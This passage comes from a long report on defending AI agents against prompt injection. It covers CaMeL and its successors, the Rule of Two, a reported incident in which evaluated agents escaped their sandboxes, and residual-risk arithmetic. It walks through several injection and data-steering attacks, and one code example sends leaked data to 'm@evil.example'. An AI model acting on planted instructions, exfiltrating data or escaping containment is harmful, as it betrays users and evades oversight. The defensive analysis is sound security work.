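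Google called its response to the findings an "Update to the Trust Model". Meged prefers this to Anthropic's approach of paying a bounty for each finding. He thinks Anthropic was right to pay and treated Novee well, but he worries that separate payments make each problem look closed while the underlying weakness remains. His point is fair, but Google's advisory shows that changing the trust model broke customers' workflows, which might make a vendor hesitate to do it. The two approaches also overlap, since Google gave its trust model change a severity score and a patched version, as it would for an ordinary flaw.

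Vendors also close reports because the product is behaving as they intended. In February 2026, the security company Mindgard reported to three vendors that their coding agents keep relying on an approval the user gave once. According to Mindgard's *Approve Once, Exploit Forever*, Anthropic closed the report as "Informative", OpenAI as "Informational", and Google as "Won't Fix", noting that the behaviour was intended. Mindgard argues that all three were wrong.

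Another security company, Adversa AI, found that Claude Code, Gemini CLI, Cursor's command-line agent and GitHub's Copilot CLI ask whether the user trusts a project's folder. If the user accepts, each one immediately starts helper programs that the project specifies. Because "yes" is the default, a malicious project can run its own code after a single keypress. Help Net Security's *One keypress is all it takes to compromise four AI coding tools* notes that programmers download unfamiliar projects all the time. Adversa concluded that this was a shared convention rather than one vendor's bug, so reporting it to each vendor separately made little sense.

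A prompt that asks about a folder, and defaults to trusting it, is weak evidence that the user agreed to run a stranger's program. Claude Code's users approve nearly every prompt, and Anthropic's own paid testers approved most of the dangerous commands they saw. Vendors can reasonably argue that someone who trusts a folder has made a decision, and that a tool that overruled its users would be hard to work with. But that argument depends on users understanding what they are accepting.

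A behaviour that is acceptable alone can also become part of an attack. Meged says that when he first reported a way to read files outside the project, Anthropic replied that this was outside its threat model, the set of attacks a product is meant to withstand, and that it had never intended the restriction as a security barrier, but that it would be interested in a way to steal data. He then combined the file reading with the published output, and Anthropic fixed this by closing the output.

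Auto mode raises the same question of what a vendor has promised. Anthropic offers a firm guarantee only for deny rules. If the classifier wrongly approves a dangerous command, such as one that deletes the user's database, that is presumably a known limitation, with a published miss rate. The same deletion would be a flaw like Google's ignored list if a deny rule should have blocked it.

Companies that use these agents should therefore be careful about relying on vulnerability databases alone. A database will show that Gemini CLI ignored its list of permitted commands, because Google accepted that as a flaw. It may omit the behaviour Mindgard reported, because none of the three vendors accepted that behaviour as a flaw.

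## Permission checks outside the model

EchoLeak and the leaks from Claude Code got past filters and approval rules that didn't check where data had come from or where it would go. *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., 2025) presents CaMeL, a design from Google DeepMind that bases its checks on both. CaMeL limits what the surrounding software will do once someone has fooled the model, but it doesn't make the model any harder to fool.

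### Two models and an interpreter

CaMeL builds on a design that Simon Willison proposed in 2023. A privileged model reads the user's request and decides which tools to call, but never reads an email, a file or a web page. A quarantined model reads that untrusted material but has no tools. It returns values that the privileged model can refer to by name without reading them.

*CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (Willison, 2025) explains a flaw that the DeepMind researchers found in Willison's own proposal. In their example, a user asks an assistant to send Bob the document he requested at their last meeting, and says that Bob's address and the document's name are in the meeting notes. The quarantined model has to read the notes to find the address. Anyone who can edit the notes can plant a different address, and the assistant will send the document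 there. The attack changes the data that one tool receives, but the same tools run.

CaMeL therefore tracks the data too. The privileged model writes its whole plan as a program in a restricted form of Python. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program, records what each value was derived from, and applies a policy before each tool call. For Bob's document, a simplified program might be:

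```python
notes    = find_notes("last meeting")
doc_name = ask_quarantined("Which document did Bob request?", notes, Text)
address  = ask_quarantined("What is Bob's email address?", notes, Email)
document = fetch_document(doc_name)
send_email(recipient=address, attachment=document)
```

The labels on each value record its sources and its permitted readers, as Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026) explain in *CaMeLoT*. Suppose the user, Bob and a colleague called Priya can open the notes, but only the user and Bob can open the document, a project budget. The interpreter would then hold these labels:

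| Value | Content | Sources | Readers |
|---|---|---|---|
| `notes` | The meeting notes | Notes file | User, Bob, Priya |
| `doc_name` | "Project budget" | Notes file, quarantined model | User, Bob, Priya |
| `address` | bob@client.example | Notes file, quarantined model | User, Bob, Priya |
| `document` | The budget | Document store, notes file, quarantined model | User, Bob |

The budget's sources include the notes because the notes determined which document the program fetched. When a value depends on several others, only people allowed to read all the others may read it.

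A policy is a short Python function that receives the tool call, its arguments and their labels. This invented one refuses to send a document to anyone who can't already open it:

```python
def check_send_email(recipient, attachment):
    if recipient.value in attachment.readers:
        return allow()
    return deny("recipient has no access to this document")
```

The policy's decision depends on what the notes contain and who can open the document:

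| Situation | Call the program makes | Decision |
|---|---|---|
| The notes are accurate | Budget to Bob | Allow |
| An attacker has replaced Bob's address | Budget to the attacker | Deny |
| The notes are accurate, but Bob can't open the budget yet | Budget to Bob | Deny |
| An attacker has replaced the document's name with that of an old price list Bob can open | Price list to Bob | Allow |

One of the two denials prevents a theft, but the other blocks what the user asked for. The software could let the user decide in both cases, but people who approve nearly every prompt may not notice an unfamiliar address. Willison describes a stricter rule that allows an email only if the recipient is trusted. Under that rule, an address taken from the notes would need the user's approval unless it was already on a list of trusted contacts.

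Separating the two models gives a stronger guarantee about which tools run. If someone adds a line to the notes telling the assistant to delete the user's files, the privileged model never reads it and the program contains no delete step for it to trigger, however the line is worded.

### Results on AgentDojo

Debenedetti and colleagues write, in a passage Willison quotes, that their approach "effectively solves the AgentDojo benchmark". In later tests, other researchers found support for this claim with regard to attacks, but they also found that the agent could no longer do much of its work.

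In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) reran CaMeL with its policies on and off, using 16 banking tasks from AgentDojo. They paired each task with nine attacks and planned three runs of each. Some attacked runs didn't finish, so the last column counts only those that did.

| Model | Policies | Harmless tasks completed | Attacks resisted |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | Off | 32 of 48 | 239 of 240 |
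| GPT-5.2 | On | 18 of 48 | 231 of 231 |
| MiMo-v2.5 | Off | 34 of 48 | 378 of 382 |
| MiMo-v2.5 | On | 18 of 48 | 357 of 357 |

With policies off, CaMeL still keeps the two models apart, and only five of 622 attacks succeeded. In about two-thirds of the pairs of task and attack, the attack needed a tool call or file that the user's task would never involve, so the separation alone should have stopped it. Turning policies on blocked the remaining attacks, but the completion rate fell to 37.5%. With only 16 tasks, the 95% confidence interval runs from about 11% to 64%.

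Other tests gave similar results. *SecureClaw* (2026) reports that an adapted version of CaMeL blocked all 629 attacks across all of AgentDojo but completed only 29 of 97 harmless tasks. SecureClaw, a rival system, completed 59, and its developers had less reason than CaMeL's to make the adapted version perform well. Garby and colleagues cite another team's figures showing that CaMeL completed seven of AgentDojo's 21 messaging tasks. So with policies on, an agent may finish only about a third of these tasks, though a different set of policies could change that considerably.

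Two of the five successful attacks got past the separation itself. The user had asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. Without ever reading the attacker's text, the privileged model wrote a loop that could call any tool depending on what the file contained, so the program would carry out the attacker's instructions.

None of these reruns included an agent with no defence at all. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, supply that comparison with a version of AgentDojo in which a central agent hands parts of each task to specialised ones. They ran 949 attacks per model in each set-up, with no policies configured. The table gives the attack success rates:

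| Model | No CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | Multi-CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |

In this test, CaMeL greatly reduced successful attacks against GPT-4.1, but no attacks succeeded against GPT-5.5 even without it. On a separate benchmark of professional tasks, running CaMeL in each agent substantially lowered the completion rate, by an average of 21.6 percentage points across the five models and by 13.4 points for GPT-5.5 and Fable 5.

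The reason to use CaMeL with a strong model is that its guarantee holds for attacks nobody has tried yet, which a benchmark can't measure. These numbers alone would give a company using GPT-5.5 little reason to adopt it, but they come from a test with fixed attacks. Peters-Gill and colleagues caution that attackers who adapt have had some success against every frontier model in a large trial.

CaMeL also gives developers the extra work of documenting the exact format that every tool returns, because its privileged model has to write code that processes a tool's result without ever reading it. An ordinary agent can look at the result before deciding how to use it.

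### Successors in 2026

Multi-CaMeL, in the last column of the table, closes a gap between agents. In one experiment, a user asked a group of three agents to send Julie a summary of some job applications on Slack. Each agent ran CaMeL. The central agent's program fetched the applications from a database through one agent, had its quarantined model summarise them, and then instructed a notification agent:

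```python
notification_agent(f"Send this summary to Julie via Slack: {summary}")
```

Somebody had planted an instruction in the database to email the data to an outside address. The central agent's privileged model never read it, but the summary became part of the message to the notification agent, which treats every message from the central agent as a user's request. The notification agent's privileged model then read the planted instruction and added the email to its program. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering, because untrusted data becomes trusted when it passes from one agent to another.

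In multi-CaMeL, a message between agents has two parts, an instruction and a set of variables. The interpreter rejects any instruction that depends on a tool's output, so the summary has to be sent as a variable, along with its labels. The receiving agent's privileged model can't read that variable. On the benchmark of professional tasks, this lowered the completion rate by a further 3.2 points on average, and by less than one point for the two strongest models.

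CaMeLoT moves some of the checks to before the program starts. CaMeL may spend a long time on a task and then refuse the last step. In an example from Nikolaou and colleagues, a security team's agent investigates an alert and then disconnects the affected computer, which requires approval from another team. If the plan has no approval step, CaMeL would find out only at the end. CaMeLoT turns the program into a map of every path it could take and checks rules against the whole map, such as:

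```
AG( call_send_money ⇒ ¬(recipient_tainted ∨ amount_tainted) )
```

`AG` means "at every point on every path", and "tainted" means that the value may derive from an untrusted source. The rule therefore forbids any path through the plan that sends money to a recipient, or in an amount, that an outsider could have chosen. If a path breaks the rule, the privileged model receives a description of that path and tries to repair the plan. CaMeLoT must assume that a loop could repeat any number of times, so it sometimes rejects a safe plan.

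Both systems depend on accurate labels, and Garby and colleagues found gaps in how CaMeL assigns them. This version of their example uses a secret bank balance:

```python
rich = True
tmp  = True
if balance > 10000:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.example", "rich")
```

If the balance is above 10,000, `tmp` becomes false and receives a secret label. The program then skips the line that changes `rich`. CaMeL labels only the assignments that run, so `rich` keeps its public label and the email goes out. Whoever receives it learns something about the balance.

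A privileged model that has read only trusted text is unlikely to write such a program by accident. Garby and colleagues found a gap that is more worrying in practice. When a program inserted an untrusted value into a longer piece of text, the interpreter treated the value as trusted. Ordinary programs insert values into text all the time.

Their own system, Randori, runs on an interpreter whose label tracking they proved correct with a proof-checking program. With GPT-5.2, Randori completed 36 of 48 harmless banking runs, twice as many as CaMeL did with its policies on. Across three models, it resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks. The proof covers the tracking, but developers still have to label the data sources correctly and put checks on the right tools.

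Agents that operate a computer through its screen are harder to protect in this way, because they normally look at the screen before every step. In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) had the privileged model write a plan in advance for everything it might encounter. These plans averaged 213 lines and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines and four branches for CaMeL's plans on AgentDojo. The system kept up to 57% of the performance that frontier models achieve without it. That is a large loss, but it may be worth accepting because attackers have been particularly successful against these agents.

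### Harm that a policy permits

Foerster and colleagues also found that an attacker can exploit a plan without adding anything to it. Most plans for browsing the web include a step that closes a cookie notice, so they put a fake notice inside an advertisement. The quarantined model reported a cookie notice there, the program clicked it, and the browser opened the attacker's site. They call this branch steering. The privileged model had written every step, but false information triggered the click.

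False data can misdirect any plan that relies on it. Bob, for example, got an old price list because of a planted document name. Labels record where a value came from but can't correct it. A careful policy can keep false data from determining anything important, but someone then has to supply the true data.

In both attacks that succeeded against Randori, the user asked the agent to read a text file and make the payment it described, but the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment. According to Garby and colleagues, the same attack succeeded in CaMeL's own evaluation, and CaMeL's designers placed it outside the attacks the system is meant to stop. The user had told the agent to follow the file's instructions. A policy that forbade this would also block the payment the user wanted.

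CaMeL also does little to prevent harm that involves no attacker, unless a policy forbids the action. Suppose the privileged model in Maria's shop misreads her request and writes a program that deletes account 48213. The account number comes from the shop's own database and Maria owns the account, so the data's labels give no reason to block the deletion. An overeager or misaligned privileged model could likewise add an unnecessary deletion to its plan. The interpreter would stop either deletion only if a policy restricted deletions, and it would then do so regardless of why the model included it.

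Much therefore depends on the policies, which someone has to write and maintain. Natural-language requests are too ambiguous to turn into policies reliably, and Willison, who has worked on application security for two decades, admits to having trouble with such rules himself. Two of the 2026 successors were tested without policies. Peters-Gill and colleagues configured none because the choice would have been arbitrary and the results would have depended on it. Foerster and colleagues left them out because the meaning of a click depends on what is on the screen. The tests therefore provide evidence about separating the models, but little about how well policies would work in an office.

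### Why labels spread

Labels cause a further problem when a model combines information. Suppose an assistant writes a weekly summary from three files and a public web page:

| Input | Readers | Trusted source? |
|---|---|---|
| Project budget | User, Bob | Yes |
| Staff rota | User, Priya | Yes |
| Supplier contract | User, Omar | Yes |
| News article | Anyone | No |
| **Summary of all four** | **User only** | **No** |

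Only the user can open all three files, so only the user may read the summary, even if the sentence Bob needs came entirely from the budget. The summary is also untrusted because it draws on the news article, so the program can't use it to decide on a payment. If the assistant saves the summary and uses it next week, the same restrictions apply to everything it writes from the summary.

In an ordinary calculation, the interpreter can work out exactly which values contributed to a result. But when a model reads several texts, nobody can reliably tell which of them influenced its answer, so a safe system has to assume that all of them did. Eventually every value carries every label, which *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* calls label explosion. The policy then has to forbid nearly everything or stop relying on labels.

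Developers can slow this down by giving the quarantined model only what it needs for each question, as in Bob's case, where it read only the notes. They can also limit the kinds of answer it may return. Red Hat describes a design in which unprivileged agents convert risky text into a few approved types of data, with no free text, before a privileged agent acts on it. A date or a yes-or-no answer leaves an attacker little room for instructions. But developers have to build these conversions separately for each application, and an agent may do worse at its task because the conversion removes some context.

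Another option is to make exceptions. Endorsement treats a piece of untrusted data as trusted for a particular purpose, and declassification releases a piece of secret data. Randori's planner can endorse data when it writes its program, before it has read anything untrusted. When Garby and colleagues removed this ability, completed runs fell from 36 to 30 of 48 with one model and from 31 to 26 with another. Without endorsement, Randori also blocked the payment attack that had succeeded when endorsement let the attacker's file through.

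Researchers are also looking for ways to estimate how much each input influenced an answer, for example by removing that input and checking whether the agent acts differently. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* lists this as an open problem. Such estimates would make labels less restrictive but would also bring back some of the uncertainty that labels were supposed to remove.

### Tokens, sandboxes and the Rule of Two

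Most companies will start with something simpler than CaMeL, such as a sandbox or a scoped token (a credential that a service accepts only for certain operations). Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) is a design rule for which abilities an agent may combine.

Under the rule, until models can reliably detect prompt injection, an agent should have no more than two of these three properties in one session: it processes untrustworthy input, it has access to sensitive systems or private data, or it can change something or communicate with the outside world. An agent that needs all three should work under supervision, for example with a person approving its actions.

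In Meta's example, an email assistant is tricked into forwarding private mail to a stranger. Removing any one of the three properties prevents the attack. The assistant could read mail only from trusted senders, work in a test environment with no private data, or send messages only to trusted recipients unless a person has checked the draft.

| Control | What it guarantees if it works correctly | What it still allows | Work it demands |
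|---|---|---|---|
| Scoped token | The service rejects operations outside the token's scope | Harmful use of a permitted operation | The service has to offer narrow scopes, and someone has to choose and issue them |
| Sandbox | A program can't reach files or addresses outside the permitted set | Misuse of anything inside it | Someone has to configure it and adjust it when a task needs more |
| Rule of Two | A planted instruction lacks one of the abilities that the worst attacks need | The agent's own mistakes, and less serious attacks | Developers have to classify every tool and data source |
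| CaMeL with policies | Untrusted text can't add steps to a plan, and the interpreter checks data before each tool call | False data, and harm that the policies permit | Developers have to write policies, label sources and document every tool's results |

Scoped tokens take the least work if the service already offers the right scope, but Railway's ordinary tokens didn't offer it in PocketOS's case. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) warns that a valid credential doesn't establish which actions someone has authorised.

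Sandboxes apply to everything a program does, including code that nobody has read. But they operate at a low level, where they may detect that a browser is contacting a shop but not whether it is viewing a product or buying it. For browser agents, Christodorescu and colleagues describe a system called ceLLMate that checks the messages the browser sends to a website. An order produces the same message whichever buttons the agent clicked. This approach takes extra work because the website's developers have to explain what each message means.

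The Rule of Two is the easiest of these to explain in a design meeting. Meta claims that following it reduces the severity of the risks "deterministically". The claim is fair when ordinary software removes one of the properties, but much less so when the remaining safeguard is human approval, since Meta itself mentions users who blindly confirm a warning. The classification can also go out of date. Red Hat, discussing a similar scheme, notes that attackers may find a way to manipulate input that was once trustworthy.

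The rule also wouldn't have prevented the deletion of PocketOS's data. As far as anyone knows, the agent had read nothing hostile. It had access to sensitive systems and could change them, which are only two of the three properties. Meta says that the rule doesn't cover an agent's mistakes or excessive privileges, and that it supplements least privilege. A company that treated the rule as a complete safety test could approve the same set-up that PocketOS had.

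A company could combine these controls by running CaMeL's interpreter inside a sandbox and giving it tokens with narrow permissions. A gap in the labels would then expose only what the tokens and the sandbox allow.

### The Hugging Face incident

Containment also failed in the OpenAI–Hugging Face incident of July 2026, in which agents under evaluation escaped their sandboxes and broke into other systems. Some critics conclude that a sufficiently capable agent will always find a weakness in whatever confines it, and that system-level controls will therefore matter less as models improve.

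*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* attributes the failure to the implementation rather than the principles. The sandboxes blocked direct connections to the internet, but a shared service for downloading software packages made requests on agents' behalf, so some requests never passed through the check. The service also stored data that supposedly separate runs could all write to, which let the agents communicate, and it gave them far wider access than downloading a package requires.

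This is a convincing account of what went wrong, and each of these faults has a known remedy. It is less convincing as a defence of containment in general. The principles describe a perfect boundary, so any escape will violate at least one of them, and the paper could give the same reply after every future incident. The critics' main question is whether people can build a boundary without such faults when the agent inside is searching for them. The paper accepts that this is difficult, especially when containment depends on large, general-purpose services.

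It recommends keeping the software that enforces the rules small and purpose-built, because less code gives an attacker fewer places to look for flaws. This is sensible advice, but small software can still be insecure. CaMeL's interpreter does a much narrower job than a package service, and Garby and colleagues still found ways for information to escape its tracking.

The incident is also weak evidence for relying on model-level safeguards instead. OpenAI had switched some of them off, so nobody knows whether they would have worked. Researchers could test the critics' claim more directly by giving capable agents plenty of time inside a small, purpose-built sandbox with no shared services and counting how often they escape.

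## How engineering, deployment and testing share the remaining risk

Even with all these measures, classifiers miss some dangerous actions, policies permit others, and sandboxes have gaps. The expected harm that remains is the residual risk. Often no single company controls it, because one trains the model, another builds the harness, a third runs the database or cloud service the agent uses, and a fourth deploys the agent.

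### Expected loss

A simple formula shows how their choices combine:

```
expected loss = dangerous attempts × miss rate × loss per completed action
```

Dangerous attempts are the harmful calls that agents make in a given period, whatever the cause. The miss rate here is the share of these calls that gets past every check, from the classifier to the database's permissions. The loss per completed action is the average damage a harmful call does when it runs, minus whatever is recovered.

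Suppose, using invented numbers, that a company's agents make 50 dangerous attempts a year and each one that runs costs £20,000 on average. The detection rates come from Anthropic's study of paid testers, who caught 13.6% of dangerous commands, compared with 89% for Claude Code's auto mode.

| Situation | Attempts | Miss rate | Loss per action | Expected loss per year |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| People approve every command | 50 | 86.4% | £20,000 | £864,000 |
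| A classifier approves commands instead | 50 | 11% | £20,000 | £110,000 |
| Better training also halves the attempts | 25 | 11% | £20,000 | £55,000 |
| The cloud service also delays deletions, so most are reversible | 25 | 11% | £2,000 | £5,500 |

Halving any of the three factors halves the expected loss, so the company can start with whichever is cheapest to change. But the estimate is only as accurate as its inputs. On ambiguous requests, Ji and colleagues measured a miss rate of 70.3% for the actions that auto mode reviewed. At that rate, the expected loss in the second row would be £703,000.

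Averages can also hide most of the risk. Suppose 49 of the 50 attempts would cost £1,000 each and the other would cost £951,000, so the average is still £20,000. If the classifier misses 10% of the small ones and has a 60% chance of missing the large one, the overall miss rate is still 11%. But the expected loss is 49 × 0.10 × £1,000 + 0.60 × £951,000, or £575,500, more than five times the figure in the table. A company should therefore calculate the expected loss separately for each kind of action and add up the results.

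Even then, £575,500 is an average. The company would usually lose either a few thousand pounds or nearly a million in a year, and a small company might not survive the larger loss. The formula also leaves out false alarms. A check that blocked every call would reduce the expected loss to zero but make the agent useless.

### Who controls each factor

| Party | Dangerous attempts | Miss rate | Loss per completed action |
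|---|---|---|---|
| Model developer | Trains the model to ignore injected instructions and stay within the task | Trains the model behind the classifier | Has little influence |
| Harness builder | Chooses which tools and text reach the model | Chooses the classifier's inputs; enforces deny rules and sandboxes | Saves earlier versions so that users can undo edits |
| Service provider | Has little influence | Offers narrow tokens and checks each request | Delays deletions and keeps backups |
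| Deploying organisation | Chooses the tasks and whose messages the agent reads | Chooses the permissions and approval mode | Keeps separate backups and gives the agent test data |

One company can have several of these roles. Anthropic trains Claude and builds Claude Code. Replit built the agent that deleted Jason Lemkin's database and ran the platform. The PocketOS incident involved four companies: Anthropic, Cursor, Railway and PocketOS.

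When the roles are separate, nobody has all the numbers for the formula. A classifier's developer can measure its miss rate over thousands of cases but doesn't know what a particular customer's database is worth. The customer knows what the database is worth but would have to see many dangerous attempts before it could measure the miss rate in its own work.

In law and economics, the "cheapest cost avoider" is the party that could have prevented an accident at the lowest cost. The table below applies this idea to ten failures. The choices are editorial judgements made in hindsight, without cost figures from the companies.

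| Case | Party that could have stopped the harm most cheaply | Change |
|---|---|---|
| LangChain's maths chain | Library developers | Evaluate arithmetic without running Python |
| Vanna's charts | Library developers | Switch off generated chart code by default |
| "Clean up old branches" | Harness builder | Ask which branches before deleting any from the server |
| PocketOS | Service provider (Railway) | Apply the dashboard's 48-hour delay to API deletions |
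| Replit | Harness builder (Replit) | Separate development databases from production |
| Instagram password resets | Deploying organisation (Meta) | Check the address against the one on file |
| EchoLeak | Harness builder (Microsoft) | Strip outside links and images from incoming messages |
| Secrets in a public GitHub log | Harness builder (Anthropic) | Stop publishing the output of commands |
| Gemini CLI's ignored command list | Harness builder (Google) | Enforce the list in every mode |
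| Break-in at Hugging Face | Organisation running the tests (OpenAI) | Limit the shared package service to downloading packages |

The choice between Railway and PocketOS is the hardest to make. PocketOS could have kept a recent copy of its data elsewhere, and it was in the best position to find the stray token on its own machine. Railway comes first because it already had the delay in its dashboard, and another customer had lost data through the same API call eleven days earlier. One change at Railway also protected all its customers, including those who had never thought about agents.

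None of the table's ten rows lists a company for its work on training a model, partly because each case is assessed separately. Repairing a harness is a cheap way to prevent one failure, while better training costs far more but reduces dangerous attempts in every product that uses the model. A company could reasonably invest in training for its total benefit across thousands of products, even if it was never the cheapest remedy for a single incident.

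### What a test with no successes can certify

Trajectory Labs made 720 injection attempts on auto mode, and none succeeded. Attacks could still succeed occasionally, since a low success rate can also produce 720 failures in a row.

If every attempt succeeds with probability *p*, independently of the others, the chance of no successes in *n* attempts is (1 − *p*)^*n*. The upper limit at 95% confidence is the value of *p* that makes this chance 5%:

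```
(1 − p)^n = 0.05,   so   p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n)
```

With 720 attempts, the limit is 0.42%. A true success rate of 1% is very unlikely, because it would produce no successes in only about one in 1,400 such tests.

But the 720 attempts were ten runs each of 72 scenarios. Runs of the same attack on the same model tend to end the same way. If they always did, the test would contain only 72 independent results, and the limit would rise to 4.1%.

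The effective number of independent attempts is probably between the number of scenarios and the total number of attempts. A common approximation divides the total by 1 + (*k* − 1)ρ, where *k* is the number of runs per scenario and ρ is the correlation between them. With ten runs per scenario and a correlation of 0.2, the 720 attempts provide about as much information as 257 independent ones.

| Correlation between runs of a scenario | Independent results | Upper limit at 95% confidence | Successes in 5,000 attacks at that limit |
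|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 720 | 0.42% | 21 |
| 0.2 | 257 | 1.2% | 58 |
| 1 | 72 | 4.1% | 204 |

The test can't show which row is right because every run ended in failure, leaving no variation from which to estimate the correlation. Testers who want a lower limit would do better to write more scenarios than to repeat the ones they have. They would need about 3,000 independent attempts without a success to get the limit down to 0.1%, and about 30,000 to reach 0.01%.

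All of these limits assume that future attacks will resemble the ones in the test. Trajectory Labs' attacks had been tuned against Claude Opus 4.7. An attacker who spends a month tuning attacks against the current model may have a much higher success rate, however many times the older attacks failed.

The test results also don't cover a changed deployment, because the test used only one set of browser tools. If a company adds a tool that sends email, an injected instruction can trigger an action that wasn't possible in the test, and the classifier has to classify a kind of call that the test may never have included.

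System-level controls need a different kind of test because a deny rule returns the same result every time it receives the same call. Trying one forbidden command would have shown that Gemini CLI's deny list was being ignored, and repeating it a thousand times would have added almost nothing. Testers should focus on looking for other routes to the same operation, such as the package service that OpenAI's agents used to get around their network restrictions.

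### What testers should report, and when to test again

A deploying organisation can't do much with an attack success rate alone. To apply a result to its own situation, it needs to know:

- how many different scenarios the testers used, how often they ran each one, and how each scenario ended
- how many harmless actions the same settings blocked
- which model the attackers practised on, and whether they could change their approach after a failure
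- the exact versions, settings, tools and permissions in the test
- separate miss rates for attacks that the developer had seen and attacks it hadn't
- the results with each defence switched off, to show which one did the work

Anthropic's August post on auto mode provides some of this. It gives the versions, Claude Code 2.1.205 and Codex 0.144.5, and the reasoning effort, which was maximum for GPT-5.6 Sol and high for the Claude models. It also compares results with and without automatic review. But the 7% miss rate on Apollo's attacks combines attacks Anthropic had seen with ones it hadn't, and the tester study has no false-alarm rate.

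Organisations should test again whenever the model, the harness, the tools, the permissions or the sources of text change. Such changes can come within weeks. Trajectory Labs tested the versions available on 17 July, and by the time Anthropic published the results on 7 August, OpenAI had released a new version of its automatic reviewer.

A repaired system should also be tested again, including on the attacks it caught before. Auto mode missed about 2% of the attacks it had previously caught after Anthropic strengthened it. A test of only the earlier misses would have shown the improvement but not the new failures.

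An agent's behaviour can change while it is in use, even without a new release. Nannini, Smith and colleagues (2026) discuss this behavioural drift in *AI Agents Under EU Law*. An agent that stores memories from past tasks, for example, may act differently in its sixth month than it did when it was tested. It makes sense to test such an agent's live configuration on a fixed schedule, even if nobody has changed anything.

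A company also can't learn from pre-release tests how many dangerous attempts to expect, but monitoring can help. David C of the National Cyber Security Centre recommends logging tool calls, including failed ones, because attackers will probably have to refine an attack before it works. A run of failed calls may be an early warning, and over time the company can use the logs to roughly estimate the first factor in the formula. The estimate will be too low if some attempts don't appear in the logs.

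### How three organisations divide the work

The Frontier Model Forum's June 2026 brief assigns duties by role. Model developers should anticipate how others will use their models and keep working on defences against prompt injection and poisoned memories. The brief is most specific about deployers, who can use sandboxes, least privilege, monitoring, checks on inputs and outputs, and audit logs. Shops and websites that agents visit may be able to detect the limits of an agent's authority. Users decide how much access to grant an agent, and greater access increases the damage it could do.

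The brief's list of roles defines companies that provide tools and harnesses but gives them no responsibilities. A later passage describes the harness as a natural place for monitoring, verification and enforcement, but doesn't make anyone responsible for doing them there. This is a serious gap because harness builders could have stopped five of the ten failures in the table more easily than anyone else. The forum's members include Anthropic, Google, Microsoft and OpenAI, all of which build harnesses.

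One example in OWASP's entry on excessive agency is an assistant that only needs to summarise email but uses an extension that can also send it. A hostile message makes the assistant search the inbox and forward what it finds. OWASP lists three changes that would each prevent this: an extension that can't send, a login with read-only access, and a rule that the user must press "send". The entry doesn't divide duties by role, but the extension's developer could make the first change, the mail service would have to support the second, and the third would take the user some time with every message. Having several remedies is useful, but it also lets each party assume that another will act.

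Android Developers' *Mitigate excessive agency vulnerabilities* applies OWASP's advice to phone apps. A model acting for a user should use that user's permissions, and the servers behind the app should check every request independently. The app should also ask before it deletes data, buys something or sends a message. Nearly all of this work falls to the app's developer, who may be one person using other companies' model, operating system and payment service.

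In a December 2025 post, David C also addresses whoever owns the risk in an organisation. He warns that prompt injection will remain a residual risk that no product can remove, and that people have to manage it when they design, build and operate a system. If the system's security can't tolerate the remaining risk, he writes, the system may not be a good use for a language model.

Neither the forum's brief nor OWASP's entry raises this option as directly. It matters most when one completed action would be disastrous and nobody can make it reversible. No realistic miss rate is low enough in that case, so the only safe choice may be to prevent the agent from performing that operation at all.

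All three recommend limits that don't depend on the model's judgement, but they differ on human approval. OWASP and the forum both recommend it for high-impact actions, though the forum worries that some approval prompts create an "illusion of oversight" because users click through them. David C doesn't include approval among his steps.

### Approving high-stakes changes by hand

Anthropic recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production infrastructure themselves. This advice seems hard to reconcile with its own tester study, in which people approved most of the dangerous commands. Fatigue can't fully explain that result, because even early in a session they caught only about 17% of those commands.

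The advice makes more sense if a person reviews a few important changes instead of every command. Claude Code can present a plan for approval before it starts work, and users reject 39% of these plans, compared with 3% of individual permission requests. They clearly pay more attention to plans. But many of the rejections probably concern the approach rather than any danger, and Anthropic hasn't published how many dangerous plans people catch.

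The value of a review depends heavily on the reviewer. In the invented company, the one very costly attempt had a 60% chance of getting past the classifier, which gave an expected loss of £570,600. A reviewer who stops half of what the classifier lets through would save about £285,000 a year. One who stops only 5%, as the testers did, would save about £28,500. The larger saving justifies a good deal of an engineer's time, but the smaller one may not.

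Switching the whole session to manual approval would be a poor way to follow Anthropic's advice, because it brings back the routine prompts and removes the classifier, which can catch the kind of change that Anthropic wants people to check. Anthropic describes a long session in which an agent tried to end processes across about two thousand pods, the units in which some computer clusters run software. The agent had also queued deletions that would have shut down training jobs on hundreds of processors. Auto mode flagged the commands before they ran. Anthropic chose this example to show its product working, so it doesn't show how often the classifier misses similar commands.

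It would be better to combine a classifier that reviews ordinary commands with a database or cloud service that requires a person to confirm the few irreversible operations. OWASP notes that a developer can put the approval step in such a downstream system, outside the language-model application. The step then applies to every agent and script with access to the service, including one that has found a stray access token.

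The request also needs to include enough information for a person to judge the command, and the bare volume ID in the PocketOS command was not enough. A useful request would include the volume's name, whether it is in production, the date of the last backup and the number of customers who depend on it. A company can measure whether its reviewers read such requests by occasionally showing them a dangerous command that won't run, as Anthropic's research vendor did.

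### What the law requires

| Law | Who has duties or may be liable | When it applies | Main limit |
|---|---|---|---|
| EU AI Act, transparency rules | Providers and deployers of systems that talk to people or generate content | From 2 August 2026 | Doesn't address whether an agent's actions are safe |
| EU AI Act, high-risk rules | Providers and deployers of high-risk systems | From 2 December 2027 for listed uses, and 2 August 2028 for certain regulated products | Doesn't cover most coding or customer-service agents |
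| EU Product Liability Directive | Mainly manufacturers of products and components, including software | To products placed on the market or put into service after 8 December 2026 | Excludes business data |
| California's AB 316 | Defendants who developed, modified or used the AI | From 1 January 2026 | Removes one defence but doesn't establish fault |

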